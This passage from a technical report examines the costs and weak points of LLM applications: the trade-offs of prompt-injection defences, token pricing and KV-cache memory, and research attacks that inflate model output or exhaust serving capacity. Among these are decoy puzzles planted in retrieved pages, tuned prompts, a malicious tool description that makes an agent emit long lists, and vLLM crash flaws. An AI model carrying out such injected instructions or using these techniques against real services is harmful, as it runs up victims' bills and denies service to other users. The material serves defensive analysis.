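People use models because models can handle requests that no developer foresaw, and strict checks take away some of that ability. When Hempel and colleagues made KAIROS refuse every action that its policy couldn't clear, it completed 42.7% of ordinary tasks, half as many as before, and stopped no more attacks than the version that held such actions for review.

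CaMeL has a similar difficulty because the model writes its plan first. Most of the failures that Peters-Gill and colleagues examined happened when a tool's result required a step that the plan didn't include. CaMeL also limits how the model can write the plan. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) notes that plans can't define their own functions, and proposes having a compiler check the agent's code before it runs. This would let the agent use nearly all of the programming language Scala.

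Better models reduce the loss in performance but haven't removed it. On a set of industrial maintenance tasks, CaMeL lowered the completion rate by 21.6 percentage points on average across five models, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. Those tests used no data policies, so the loss came from planning in advance. On computer-operating tasks, Foerster and colleagues kept up to 57% of the performance of larger models when they counted a task as done if any of five plans succeeded, but 28% with only one plan.

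Some of the lost tasks are hard for any defence to make safe. Many of AgentDojo's banking tasks require the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, which is also what an attacker wants. FIDES blocks most of these tasks by design. KAIROS lets its reviewing model decide, and the rewritten attacks that got past it exploited tasks of this kind. A user who lets a document direct the agent must either trust everyone who can edit the document or approve each consequential action personally. Costa and colleagues point out that people tire of frequent approval requests and stop reading them.

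The objection is strongest for agents with open-ended work. On such tasks, the agent protected by KAIROS completed 51.7% when there was no attack, close to the unprotected agent's 53.3%. Under attack, the protected agent completed 37.1% and the unprotected one 55.5%, largely because later steps depended on actions KAIROS was still holding. The objection is much weaker for the shop's chat box. Customers need the model to understand oddly worded questions and answer them clearly, and they lose nothing if it can fetch only listed pages and look up only their own orders. The developer can leave the wording unrestricted and put the strict checks on the few actions that change a record, spend money or send data out.

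## What a request costs in computing and money

Most of the checks described so far run after the model has written its reply, and by then the shop already owes money for it. The bill depends on how many tokens the model reads and how many it writes.

### Reading the prompt and writing the reply

A model call has two stages. In the first, called prefill, the model processes the prompt. The whole prompt is available from the start, so the processor can work on thousands of tokens at once. In the second, called decoding, the model writes its reply one token at a time, because each token depends on the ones before it.

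Decoding uses the hardware inefficiently. A model consists of billions of numbers, called parameters, and in a conventional design the processor has to read all of them from memory at every step. A model with 70 billion parameters of 2 bytes each takes up 140 GB. One pass through those 140 GB can process a prompt of several thousand tokens during prefill, but produces only one token during decoding for a single user, when the processor spends most of its time waiting for data. This is the main technical reason output usually costs more than input, though the exact ratio is a commercial decision.

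Many models also generate reasoning tokens while working out an answer. Customers never see this text, but it is usually billed as output. For example, eesel's *Claude Opus 5 pricing in 2026* lists "thinking" under the output price. Developers can often choose how much a model reasons, but they can't always turn reasoning off. According to TrustList's software directory entry *GPT-6.2 Astra*, OpenAI's newest large model rejects any request that sets reasoning to none.

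### Batching and the KV cache

Providers recover much of the wasted capacity through batching, which means processing several users' requests together. One pass through the parameters can produce the next token for each of 50 users. Older systems held a batch together until its longest reply was finished. With continuous batching, each request leaves the batch as soon as its reply is finished, and a waiting request takes its place.

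Wang, Fan and colleagues (2026), in *Rethinking Latency Denial-of-Service*, measured how much long-winded requests slow down replies to other users. They ran a small model, Qwen3-8B, on one processor and made 50 to 75% of the requests deliberately long-winded. Other users waited only 3 to 5.7% longer for their replies to begin, but each token after that took about 7% longer.

That slowdown comes from data that the requests can't share. To continue a text, a model relates the newest token to all the earlier ones in a calculation called attention. In each layer of the model, every token has a key, which determines how relevant it is to later tokens, and a value, which holds the information it contributes. Each layer repeats the calculation in several parallel units called heads. The keys and values of earlier tokens stay the same as the text grows, so the serving program stores them instead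 of computing them again. This store is the KV cache, and its size is

bytes per token = 2 × layers × key-value heads × head size × bytes per number

where the 2 stands for one key and one value. A model with 80 layers, 8 key-value heads, a head size of 128 and 2 bytes per number needs 327,680 bytes for each token. For a text of 100,000 tokens, that comes to about 33 GB, all for one user.

If the processors have 320 GB of memory between them and the parameters take up 140 GB, the remaining 180 GB has room for about 270 conversations of 2,000 tokens, or five of 100,000. Each decoding step reads the parameters and the stored keys and values, roughly 300 GB in either case, but it produces 270 tokens with the short conversations and five with the long ones. These figures are illustrative, and many newer designs store less per token, but a long text always takes up room that other requests could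 have used. When the memory is full, the serving program either makes new requests wait or interrupts a running one, whose stored data it must then move elsewhere or compute again.

### The price formula

Customers who use a model through a provider see none of this directly. They pay

cost = input tokens × input price + output tokens × output price

OpenAI applies a third rate to cached input, which is text that the provider has processed recently and kept in store. The table gives standard list prices in dollars per million tokens, from Anthropic's *Claude Fable 5.2*, Anthropic's *Pricing* and OpenAI's *Flagship models*, with TrustList's figures for GPT-6.2 Astra:

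| Model | Input | Cached input | Output |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.2 | 8.00 | 0.20 | 40.00 |
| GPT-6.2 Astra | 8.00 | 0.40 | 40.00 |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | 4.00 | 0.20 | 20.00 |
| Claude Sonnet 5.5 | 2.00 | 0.20 | 10.00 |
| GPT-6 Luna | 0.10 | 0.01 | 0.50 |

For all five, output costs five times as much as input.

Suppose the furniture shop uses Claude Opus 5.5. The question about the bench takes two calls. The first reads 3,000 tokens and writes a tool call of 50. The second reads 3,200, because the prompt now includes the tool call and the delivery date, and writes an answer of 100. Together they cost

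6,200 × $4/1,000,000 + 150 × $20/1,000,000 = $0.0248 + $0.0030 = $0.0278

or just under 3 cents. A thousand such questions a day would cost about $28, and on GPT-6 Luna about 70 cents. If Opus also wrote 2,000 reasoning tokens per question, that would add 4 cents and more than double the bill, although the customer would see the same sentence.

Tools add to the cost of a request. The model reads a description of each tool in every call, and Anthropic's set of tools for operating a web browser adds about 6,600 tokens to a request. Each web search costs a cent, plus the price of the tokens it returns. The price also depends on how quickly the customer needs the answer. Both companies charge half price for large jobs that can wait and double for fast mode, on the models that offer it.

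Anthropic charges the same rate per token for a prompt of 900,000 tokens as for one of 9,000. TrustList reports that OpenAI charges twice the usual input rate and 1.5 times the usual output rate for GPT-6.2 Astra requests with more than 272,000 input tokens, and that the higher rates apply to the whole request. OpenAI's pricing probably matches the computing resources used more closely, because long texts occupy a lot of memory, but the bill could surprise a developer who doesn't know about the surcharge.

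### How a long run becomes expensive

The shop's program resends the whole prompt on every pass through its loop. If the starting text has S tokens and each step adds d more, the first call reads S tokens, the second S + d, the third S + 2d, and so on. Over n calls, the total input is

nS + dn(n−1)/2

In *Persistent Billable State*, Zhang, Xia and colleagues (2026) derive the same total for agents that keep the results of their tool calls. The second term grows with the square of the number of calls, so doubling the number of calls in a long run roughly quadruples its input.

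Here is what that means for an agent on Claude Opus 5.5 that starts with 5,000 tokens and adds 2,000 at each step:

| Calls | Input tokens | Input cost without caching | Input cost with caching |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10 | 140,000 | $0.56 | $0.14 |
| 50 | 2.7 million | $10.80 | $1.03 |
| 100 | 10.4 million | $41.60 | $3.05 |
| 200 | 40.8 million | $163.20 | $10.09 |

Output adds little to the cost of such a run. If each call produces 300 output tokens, 100 calls produce 30,000, which cost 60 cents. Output is more expensive per token than input, but the agent writes each token once and may read it a hundred times.

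The last column assumes prompt caching works perfectly. With caching, the provider keeps the processed form of a prompt after the call ends. If the next prompt begins with the same text, the model only has to process what is new. On Opus 5.5, storing text for five minutes costs $5 per million tokens, a quarter more than ordinary input, and reading it back costs 20 cents per million. In the run of 100 calls, the agent stores each of 203,000 tokens once, for $1.02, and reads about 10.2 million tokens from the cache, for $2.04.

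A developer can easily lose this discount. The stored keys and values depend on everything that came before them, so a change near the beginning of the prompt makes everything stored after it unusable. A program that puts the current time at the top of its prompt would lose the discount on every call. If it also asked the provider to store each new version, the 100 calls would cost $52, more than without caching. The discount can also be lost when a tool takes longer than five minutes to answer, unless the developer pays $8 per million tokens for an hour's storage.

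Even perfect caching only lowers the price per token. The agent still reads 10.4 million tokens, and the part of the bill that comes from rereading still grows with the square of the number of calls. To slow that growth, the developer has to shorten the history. Zhang and colleagues ran the same agents with the full history, with earlier tool results deleted, and with those results compressed. Keeping the full history raised the average cost of a session by 21.2 to 35.9%, even after cache discounts. But on tasks that depended on the earlier results, the agent completed only 2 of 12 after deletion with each of two providers' models, compared with 10 and 11 of 12 after compression. Shortening the history can therefore save a modest amount at some risk to the work, and a developer would have to test whether the agent can do without what compression removes.

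### Small requests with large bills

The shop pays for everything the customer's question about the bench triggers, while the customer pays nothing for the answer. OWASP's 2026 list emphasises this cost asymmetry.

A short question can lead to a long answer. GPT-6.2 Astra can write up to 128,000 tokens in one reply, which would cost $5.12 at the standard rate. Few legitimate questions come near that limit, but some attacks try to push a model towards it. A short question can also come with a long prompt if the application lets a visitor upload a file or point to a web page. A call with the largest input that GPT-6.2 Astra accepts, 922,000 tokens, and the longest possible reply would cost about $22.43, including the surcharge.

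An agent can multiply the cost again by rereading what it has fetched. Anthropic estimates that a research paper in PDF form is about 125,000 tokens. Suppose a visitor asks the agent in the table to read one, and the agent fetches it in its tenth call. Without caching, the agent would reread the paper in each of the remaining 90 calls of a 100-call run. That would add 11.25 million tokens and $45, so the visitor's one-sentence request would more than double the cost of the run. With caching, the paper would add less than $3.

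The effect of a long request depends on who runs the model. If a shop pays a provider by the token, the provider's processors handle the extra work and the shop gets a larger bill, which can amount to denial of wallet. If the shop runs the model on its own processors, its bill may hardly change, but long requests fill the memory and make other customers wait, which can amount to denial of service.

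High spending doesn't by itself mean that anything has gone wrong. OpenAI's *Research acceleration* (2026), published in November, reported that the company's median researcher used $2,400 of AI a day at list prices. In mid-August, the figure was just over $600, according to Fortune (2026). Emberson's *Coding-agent use at OpenAI is doubling roughly every month* found a similar rate of growth. OpenAI doesn't pay its own list prices, and its researchers aren't typical customers, but another company would pay about $2,400 a day for the same use. That would cover about 58 of the uncached 100-call runs in the table, or nearly 800 of the cached ones.

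At the shop, $2,400 would pay for about 86,000 questions about benches, so a one-day bill of that size would almost certainly mean an attack or a fault. A spending cap low enough to protect the shop would stop an OpenAI researcher's work within minutes.

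## Inputs that make a request unusually expensive

The shop pays about 3 cents to answer a question about a bench, but the longest reply that GPT-6.2 Astra can write costs $5.12. For several years, researchers have been looking for inputs that make a model write longer, more expensive replies.

This work began with *Sponge Examples* (Shumailov and colleagues, 2021), before chatbots were common. The researchers tried to increase a model's energy use and running time, whereas most earlier attacks on neural networks tried to cause wrong answers. When they had access to a model's internals, they looked for inputs that raised its activations, the numbers that each layer passes to the next. Some hardware saves energy by skipping zeros, so an input that leaves fewer zeros takes more energy to process. They also used a genetic algorithm, which keeps the best inputs found so far, recombines and alters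 them, and tests the results. *Inducing Overthink* (Wang, Cao and colleagues, 2026) reports that the largest slowdown was 6,000-fold, on a real translation service.

That figure is a poor guide to current chat models. Miao, Cao and colleagues (2026) point out in *Chatter Attack* that Shumailov's method suited an older design used in translation systems. In a chat model, the cost of a reply depends mostly on its length, so later attacks are designed to make the model write more.

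### How a reply ends

Nothing fixes the length of a reply in advance. The program that runs the model adds one token at a time:

```python
while len(reply) < limit:
    token = next_token(prompt + reply)
    if token == END:
        break
    reply.append(token)
```

At each step, the model gives every token in its vocabulary a probability, and the program uses these probabilities to pick one. One of these tokens, the end-of-sequence token, has no visible text and marks the end of the reply. Generation stops when the program picks this token or when the reply reaches the length limit.

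If the end token had the same probability h at every step, the average reply would be 1/h tokens long. Lowering h from 1% to 0.1% would lengthen it from 100 tokens to 1,000. With a limit of B tokens, the average is

(1 − (1 − h)^B)/h

For h = 0.01% and a limit of 4,096 tokens, that comes to about 3,360 instead of 10,000. Miao and colleagues use the same sum to relate their attack to the expected length of a reply.

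The probability that a model ends its output is close to zero in the middle of a sentence and much higher after a complete answer. An attacker can therefore try to lower it directly, or give the model so much work that it takes a long time to reach a natural ending.

### Strings tuned to a model's internals

Dong and colleagues (2025), in *An Engorgio Prompt Makes Large Language Model Babble On*, used a model's parameters to find input strings that lower the end token's probability throughout the reply. An outsider can do this only if the model's developer has published the parameters. On open models with up to 30 billion parameters, the strings made replies roughly 2 to 13 times as long as usual, often close to the length limit.

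Engorgio has performed less well in other researchers' tests. When Miao and colleagues tried it on a 7-billion-parameter version of DeepSeek-R1, the average answer to a school maths problem grew from 424 tokens to 569. On OpenAI's gpt-oss-20b, it grew from 253 to 850. These figures may understate Engorgio's effect, because Miao and colleagues were presenting a new attack and had little reason to optimise an old one.

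According to Miao and colleagues, a search for a way to control thousands of tokens can fail because the model picks tokens partly at random, and one unexpected choice can be enough to derail it. Their Chatter Attack targets only the opening of the reply and is designed to make it a short expression of doubt. It is also designed to keep the model's attention on that opening later, so that the model keeps producing text that questions its earlier work.

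With full access to the 7-billion-parameter model, the attack lengthened the average answer on the same maths problems from 424 tokens to 13,346. The paper emphasises this 31.5-fold increase, which is by far the largest. On those problems, the increase was about 8-fold for gpt-oss-20b and 3-fold for the larger QwQ-32b. The 7-billion-parameter model's accuracy also fell, from 99.4% to 70.4%, mainly because many replies reached the 16,384-token limit before giving an answer. A developer who monitors for unfinished replies would have a good chance of noticing the attack.

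### Decoy tasks and unanswerable questions

In the OverThink attack (Kumar et al., 2025), the attacker hides a demanding puzzle in a web page or document that an application is likely to retrieve. When someone asks about the page, the model works through the puzzle as well as the question. At the furniture shop, the puzzle could be in a product review. The attacker doesn't need access to the model or even an account.

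This is indirect prompt injection, but the answer the customer sees can still be correct. The extra work is in the hidden reasoning tokens. Kumar and colleagues tested OpenAI's o1, o1-mini and o3-mini, and DeepSeek-R1. With a decoy, the models used up to 18 times as many reasoning tokens on one set of questions and up to 46 times as many on another.

OverThink also did worse when Miao and colleagues ran it on small open models. At best, it roughly doubled the length of the 7-billion-parameter model's answers to school maths problems, and one version of the attack shortened QwQ-32b's answers from 991 tokens to 807. The decoy puzzles are mostly handmade, so one that lengthens a model's answers may not work on other models.

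Honest users can also cause long replies by leaving out a fact the model needs. Fan and colleagues (2025) made a set of maths problems that each lack a necessary fact. When Wang, Cao and colleagues gave DeepSeek-R1 the versions based on competition problems, its average reply grew from 355 tokens to 4,323. The model usually kept looking for an answer instead of replying that the problem had none. A customer who asks whether a bench will fit on the patio, without giving the patio's size, is asking the same kind of question. Gemini 2.5 Flash, however, wrote shorter replies than usual when simple arithmetic problems were missing a fact.

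### Searching from outside

Most commercial providers keep their models' parameters secret, so an attacker has to find expensive inputs by experiment. *ThinkTrap* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2025) needed only to send text to a model and count the tokens in each reply, and it used that count to decide what to try next. The inputs it found were only 20 tokens long.

The researchers tested ThinkTrap on eight models, ranging from the 3-billion-parameter Llama 3.2 to Gemini 2.5 Pro, DeepSeek R1 and an OpenAI model they call GPT-o4. They compared it with four other methods: difficult open-ended questions, the same questions with a request for more detail, and two older searches that change individual words, one from *Sponge Examples*. On seven of the models, ThinkTrap needed less searching than the others to produce long replies. On Llama 3.2, the *Sponge Examples* search did better when the budget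 was small.

For Gemini 2.5 Pro, DeepSeek R1 and two other models, a search that used 10,000 tokens was enough to find an input that produced a reply of about 4,000 tokens. The search cost about 10 cents on Gemini, about 2 cents on DeepSeek and 44 cents on the OpenAI model. The researchers cut off every reply at 4,096 tokens, so nobody knows how much longer the models would have continued. A reply of that length would cost the shop about 8 cents on Claude Opus 5.5, so an attacker who pays for the search has to reuse the input many times to do much damage.

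An input that works on one model often fails on another. Li and colleagues tuned inputs to an 8-billion-parameter Llama model that DeepSeek had trained further. When they tried these inputs on other Llama models, those models answered with fewer than 800 tokens. The inputs worked much better on models that had learned from the same DeepSeek data. The researchers conclude that the weakness probably comes from this later training, which would explain why models with the same architecture don't share it.

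In *Prompt-Induced Over-Generation as Denial-of-Service*, Manu, Guo and colleagues (2025) set out to compare such searches on equal terms. Their main measure, the over-generation factor, is the number of tokens in the reply divided by the size of the model's context window. They tested an evolutionary search and a small neural network that learns to write inputs by trial and error. In the main tests of the network, they let replies run to 16,384 tokens.

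The network raised the average factor from 0.66 to 2.70 on Phi-3-mini and from 0.36 to 2.04 on Llama 2 7B. On Phi-3-mini, 46% of the replies reached the limit without producing an end token, compared with 2.3% for ordinary inputs. On a 13-billion-parameter chat version of Llama 2, the average rose only from 0.09 to 0.50, and none of the replies reached the limit.

These are small models from 2023 and 2024, and the benchmark includes none with 30 billion parameters or more. The benchmark's measure also works poorly for current commercial models. GPT-6.2 Astra, for example, accepts far more text than it can generate, so even its longest possible reply would have a factor well below 1.

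### Results on commercial models

Wang, Cao and colleagues applied a genetic algorithm to reasoning models. They split maths problems into facts and questions, then mixed parts of different problems. The search took about 60 queries per model and kept the versions that led to the longest replies with the most signs of hesitation, such as self-correction. On competition problems, DeepSeek-R1's longest reply grew from 467 tokens to 12,206, a 26-fold increase.

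Miao and colleagues also tested commercial services. For o3 and DeepSeek-R1, they reused strings that they had found on small open models. For DeepSeek-V4-Pro, they used a version of Chatter Attack designed for models whose internals are hidden. Both groups used GSM8K, a set of school-level word problems, so it allows a rough comparison:

| Service | Attack | Average tokens, ordinary | Average tokens, attacked | Increase |
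|---|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-R1 | Genetic search | 343 | 4,121 | 12.0× |
| DeepSeek-R1 | Chatter Attack, reused strings | 854 | 1,060 | 1.2× |
| DeepSeek-V4-Pro | Chatter Attack, hidden-model version | 240 | 2,860 | 11.9× |
| Qwen3-Thinking | Genetic search | 765 | 4,082 | 5.3× |
| o3 | Genetic search | 367 | 1,405 | 3.8× |
| o3 | Chatter Attack, reused strings | 363 | 798 | 2.2× |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | Genetic search | 530 | 987 | 1.9× |

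The ratios depend heavily on the baseline. The two groups' figures for ordinary replies from DeepSeek-R1 differ by a factor of 2.5. Even within *Inducing Overthink*, the model's ordinary replies to the same set of simple arithmetic problems average 202 tokens in one test and 685 in another.

Easy questions also make an attack look stronger, because the same number of extra tokens is a larger multiple of a short answer. DeepSeek-V4-Pro answers a school maths problem in 240 tokens. Its replies to terminal tasks were already 5,980 tokens long, and the attack raised that to 15,316, which is only 2.6 times as long but adds more than 9,000 tokens. The victim pays for the extra tokens, so their number matters more than the ratio.

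DeepSeek-V4-Pro, with 1.6 trillion parameters, is probably the best guide to current commercial models. The other services in the table run models from 2025. None of these studies tested attacks on GPT-6, Gemini 4 or any Claude model, so it is unknown how well the methods work on them.

The attacker may not need to search for optimised strings. In their study of serving systems, Wang, Fan and colleagues also tested ordinary-language requests for long pieces of writing with many required parts. On Qwen3-8B, more than 85% of these produced replies at least ten times as long as the request. They cost 100 to 500 times less to prepare than optimised strings, and a filter for unnatural text won't detect them. The shop's chat box would be vulnerable to such requests if it wrote whatever a visitor asked for.

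### Whether long replies delay other users

A long reply always costs money, but Wang, Fan and colleagues dispute that it does much harm to other users of the same server. They measured short delays even when most requests produced long replies, which they attribute to continuous batching. If a server handles 16 requests at once, an endless reply takes up one place and leaves the other 15 for everyone else.

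They also derive a bound on the delay. As long as memory and processing capacity are available, one long request adds no more to another user's average wait than the time needed to read its prompt, divided by the number of places. If reading the prompt takes 100 milliseconds and there are 16 places, the bound is about 6 milliseconds, whether the reply has 100 tokens or 100,000.

The bound no longer applies when the KV cache is full. With the default settings, which the researchers used, vLLM admits requests in the order they arrive. If the server has 1 GB of free memory and the next request needs 2 GB, every request behind it has to wait, including a short question that needs only a few megabytes.

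When a running request needs more memory and none is left, vLLM interrupts the request it admitted most recently. To resume that request, it has to recompute the keys and values for the prompt and everything the model had written so far. If the server is almost full, a few more tokens from the attacker can therefore force it to recompute thousands of tokens for another user's request.

Wang, Fan and colleagues' attack, Fill and Squeeze, first fills the memory with long replies and then keeps the server close to this point with shorter ones. The attacker can't see how full the memory is but can estimate it, because everyone's replies slow down as it fills. The researchers tested the attack on a single processor with 48 GB of memory. They compared it with Engorgio and two newer methods: LoopLLM, which traps a model in repetition, and ExtendAttack, which adds tedious steps to its reasoning.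 The table shows how many seconds other users waited, on average, for a reply to begin:

| Model | No attack | Engorgio | LoopLLM | ExtendAttack | Fill and Squeeze |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-8B | 0.15 | 0.12 | 1.80 | 0.85 | 11.05 |
| Gemma3-12B | 0.13 | 0.13 | 3.46 | 10.55 | 97.83 |
| DeepSeek-R1-Distill-Llama-8B | 0.08 | 0.10 | 1.07 | 13.29 | 5.31 |

On Qwen3-8B, each token after the first took more than five times as long as usual. One percent of users waited more than six minutes for a reply to begin.

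These results only partly support the paper's claim that attacks on output length are "largely ineffective" against modern serving systems. Engorgio caused no delay, but ExtendAttack made Gemma's users wait more than ten seconds and did more harm than Fill and Squeeze on the DeepSeek model. Fill and Squeeze can use ExtendAttack's inputs in place of ordinary requests, and the combination caused the longest waits on all three models. On SGLang, another popular serving program, LoopLLM delayed Gemma's users by 267 seconds, compared with 212 for Fill and Squeeze. SGLang sets aside room for up to 4,096 future tokens when it admits a request, so long replies use up the available room even sooner.

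Attacking output length and attacking the scheduler are less distinct than the paper suggests, since long replies fill the memory. Timing does make long replies more effective. On Qwen3-8B, Fill and Squeeze cost $0.75 and LoopLLM $0.80, but Fill and Squeeze caused a delay six times as long.

More hardware makes the attack harder, and it failed when the researchers spread the model over eight processors because the attacker could no longer fill the memory. The attack is easier during busy periods, when ordinary customers take up some of the memory. Simulated customer traffic, modelled on real usage records, lowered the attacker's cost by about 40%.

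### ThinkTrap's load tests

Li and colleagues report that ThinkTrap cut a service's throughput to as little as 1% of normal with only ten requests a minute. They measured this on their own servers, although the paper's summary gives the result alongside tests of commercial services. They sent the commercial services only a limited number of queries to avoid disrupting them.

The first server ran an 8-billion-parameter model on four RTX 2080 Ti graphics cards, consumer hardware from 2018. It used Transformers, a general library for running models, instead of a dedicated serving program such as vLLM. Each of the first 40 inputs added about four minutes of computation, so at ten inputs a minute, the server received about 40 minutes of work every minute. After about 80 inputs, it ran out of memory and many requests failed.

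This server would probably have slowed down under ordinary customers' requests too. It slowed down significantly even when the researchers limited replies to 256 tokens. Ten such replies a minute come to only about 43 tokens a second, while the vLLM server in Miao and colleagues' tests produced about 79 tokens a second with a model of similar size.

The result from the second server is harder to dismiss. This server ran a 70-billion-parameter model on eight Huawei Ascend processors with a total of 512 GB of memory, and took requests in order of arrival. The parameters would take up about 140 GB. A reply of 32,768 tokens, the limit in the first test, needs about 11 GB of KV cache for a model of this design, so roughly 35 such replies would fill the remaining memory. The server collapsed after several tens of inputs, even with a detector that stopped repetitive replies.

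That estimate is rough, but it suggests that the server failed because of a full memory and a strict queue, as Wang, Fan and colleagues say. Changing the scheduler also helped. When each request could generate only 1,024 tokens before going to the back of the queue, a single attacker could no longer bring down the service. Several attackers at once could still cause long waits, and legitimate users waited longer for long replies.

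In their own test, Miao and colleagues made 10% of the requests to their vLLM server Chatter Attack queries. The average number of requests running at once rose from 2.2 to 17.4, but the KV cache was only 17% full. Other users waited 40 milliseconds for a reply to begin, up from 22, and the text then arrived about a quarter more slowly. Few users would notice the extra 18 milliseconds, though the researchers describe the effect as a substantial burden on the server.

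Long replies can therefore stop a server that has little memory relative to the reply length it allows, especially if it handles requests strictly in order. A company that runs a model on one or two processors has reason to take this seriously. Evidence is missing for large providers because none of these studies measured the effect on a commercial provider's other customers, and such a test could itself cause an outage.

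### Requests that crash the serving software

A request can also take down a server even if the model writes little. Serving programs offer many options besides plain text, and the code for each one can fail. vLLM's security advisories from 2025 and 2026 describe several examples.

vLLM can force a reply to fit a schema or a regular expression (a compact notation for patterns in text) that the customer's program sends with the request. According to advisories from May 2025, an invalid schema (CVE-2025-48942) or an invalid regular expression (CVE-2025-48943) could crash the whole server. A third flaw, CVE-2025-48944, involved malformed patterns and types in the description of a tool. One such request crashed the process that runs the model, which stayed down until someone restarted it. All three affected versions from 0.8.0 and were fixed in 0.9.0.

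The shop's customers couldn't trigger these flaws through the chat box, because the developer writes the schemas and tool descriptions. The risk is much greater for a company that gives outsiders direct access to vLLM or lets users define their own tools.

Another flaw, CVE-2025-48887, could make a vLLM server extremely slow or unavailable. vLLM uses a regular expression to find tool calls that a model writes in the style of Python code. Some regular expressions can match the same text in so many ways that each additional character may double the work, in which case 30 more characters would multiply it by about a billion. The text that triggers this slowdown comes from the model, so this is an output-handling flaw that leads to unbounded consumption.

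According to a March 2025 advisory (CVE-2025-29770), a stream of very short requests, each with a different schema, could eventually fill a vLLM server's disk because one component saved every new schema there without limiting the total. In January 2026, vLLM's maintainers disclosed that a single specially made one-pixel image could shut down a server running certain models that accept images (CVE-2026-22773). Version 0.12.0 fixed that flaw.

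Limits on tokens and spending do little against flaws like these, because a harmful request may use fewer tokens and cost less than an ordinary one. The operator has to install updates that fix them, and the serving program has to reject a malformed request without interrupting other users' requests.

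## Agents that repeat or multiply their own work

An agent can run up a large bill even when every reply is short, because it can keep calling the model. This often happens without an attack.

### How a loop decides to continue

Many agents, like the shop's chat program, keep calling the model until a reply contains no tool call, so the model's output determines how many times the model runs. Training makes a model likely to stop once it has an answer, but doesn't guarantee that it will.

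Checks on the output can add loops of their own. Suppose the developer replaces `eval` in the price calculator with a parser that accepts only sums, and has the program try again when the parser rejects a reply:

```python
def get_sum(question):
    prompt = question
    while True:
        reply = call_model(prompt)
        if is_sum(reply):
            return reply
        prompt = prompt + " Reply with a sum only."
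```

Retrying helps when failures are random, but not when every attempt fails for the same reason. If the parser rejects 5% of replies at random, the average question takes 1/(1 − 0.05), or about 1.05 calls, and the developer will probably never see a long run of retries. But if a customer asks whether the bench is comfortable, there is no sum to write, so the model may answer with a sentence every time, and the parser will reject each one.

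An agent may also continue because it can't verify that it has finished. If its task is to find the lowest price for a bench anywhere on the web, there is always another shop to check. Two agents can keep each other running if each is programmed to answer every message, even a thank-you. A tool can also keep an agent running if every result includes a request for another call, as when search results never reach a last page.

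### Endless loops in published projects

In *When Agents Do Not Stop*, Hou, Wang and colleagues (2026) looked for such loops in 6,549 open-source Python agent projects. They counted a loop as a flaw if it could keep making costly calls or adding to stored text without an effective limit. An exit that depends on the model's reply, like the one in `get_sum`, did not count as a limit.

Many of these loops are hard to find because the code doesn't contain a `while` statement. In LangGraph, a popular framework for building agents, developers define steps and the connections between them, and a connection back to an earlier step creates a loop. The researchers' scanner, IAL-Scan, therefore starts by translating projects from any of eight frameworks into a common description of their model calls, tools, stored text and limits. It then builds a graph from these parts, finds paths that return to their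 starting point, and checks whether a limit applies to each.

A limit on an agent's work has to apply to the outermost loop that can repeat that work. Suppose an agent may take at most ten steps, but an outer program restarts it whenever a second model rejects its answer. The count begins again with each restart, so the total number of steps has no limit.

The scan found 340 candidates, which GPT-5.5 narrowed to 74. Two of the researchers then read the code and confirmed 68 flaws in 47 projects:

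| What repeats | Flaws | Projects |
|---|---|---|
| Retries after an error or a rejected reply | 17 | 10 |
| Tool calls | 16 | 11 |
| Messages between agents | 14 | 13 |
| Steps in a workflow that leads back to itself | 9 | 8 |
| Messages that re-enter the same agent | 7 | 2 |
| Agents that run, delegate to or evaluate other agents | 5 | 4 |

One of the flaws was in a sample customer-service assistant published by NVIDIA. If the model returned an empty reply, the program added a message asking for a real output and called the model again, with no limit on attempts. Another project, LiteRAG, asked the model for a plan, ignored any error in reading it, and asked again until it got one it could use.

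In NVIDIA's assistant, each attempt lengthens the prompt, so the context window would eventually stop the loop. The researchers found this kind of growth in only 19 of the 68 flaws, so the other 49 may lack even this unintended limit.

Hou and colleagues confirmed the flaws by reading code, so their count doesn't show how often these loops run out of control in practice. The scanner also missed seven flaws that the researchers found when they checked the alerts from two simpler methods. GPT-5.5's filtering varied between runs, with two repeats keeping only 64 and 60 of the 68 confirmed flaws. The study leaves out cases where an agent makes no progress for reasons that aren't visible in the code, such as the endless search for a cheaper bench.

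### Tools that prolong a successful task

An endless loop usually leaves the user without an answer, so the problem is at least visible. In *Beyond Max Tokens*, Zhou, Zheng and colleagues (2026) designed an attack that changes only the cost, while the user still gets the right answer.

An attacker controls an MCP server connected to an agent. The attacker keeps the tool's name and function but adds an instruction to its description to supply a step number and a long, useless list with each call. Until the last step, the server returns a progress notice that leads the model to make the next call. If the model shortens the list, the server requests the full version. At the last step, it returns the real result. A cap on the length of each model reply doesn't prevent this, because the model can produce many replies that each stay under the cap.

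The researchers used an automated search to refine the wording of the tool's text for each model. They then ran the attack on six models, with tasks from two collections that normally need one tool call. These are the results for one collection, ToolBench:

| Model | Output tokens, ordinary | Output tokens, attacked | Increase | Tasks completed, ordinary | Attack worked and task completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
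| Llama 3.3 70B | 260 | 81,830 | 315× | 98.1% | 96.2% |
| Qwen3 32B | 638 | 65,273 | 102× | 94.6% | 80.5% |
| GLM-4.5-Air | 634 | 63,694 | 100× | 95.0% | 83.1% |
| Mistral Large | 127 | 61,354 | 483× | 90.8% | 81.2% |
| Llama-DeepSeek 70B | 197 | 65,546 | 333× | 86.6% | 78.9% |
| Seed 32B | 1,298 | 85,037 | 66× | 90.4% | 84.3% |

The largest increase was 658-fold, from 87 tokens to 57,255, on Mistral Large with the other collection. At Claude Opus 5.5's price, the cost of the output in the Llama row would rise from about half a cent to $1.64.

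As with attacks on single replies, a short baseline inflates the ratio. In an agent that already makes a hundred calls, the same tool would add a similar number of tokens but increase the total by a far smaller percentage. The tests also ran in a simulator with fixed tool results, and none of the six models is among today's leading commercial ones.

The attack also slowed other work on the same hardware. With 25 queries running at once on eight processors, the KV cache peaked at 35 to 74% full, compared with a normal peak of less than 1% in most cases. A separate, harmless workload ran at about half its usual speed.

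Models that screen for unsafe behaviour flagged fewer than 3% of the attacked runs. This isn't surprising, since a long list of numbers is not unsafe content and the task ends correctly. *OTora*, a study of agents that shop, handle email and operate a computer, similarly found that its attacks increased hidden reasoning tokens by up to 10 times while the agents completed their tasks almost as accurately as before.

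### Paying again for stored results

Zhou and colleagues counted only the tokens that the model writes, but an agent that keeps its history also rereads them on every later call. Suppose Llama's 81,830 tokens came from six tool calls of equal length. The later calls, including the one that writes the final answer, would reread about 286,000 tokens of earlier lists. On Opus 5.5 without caching, that would add $1.15 to the $1.64.

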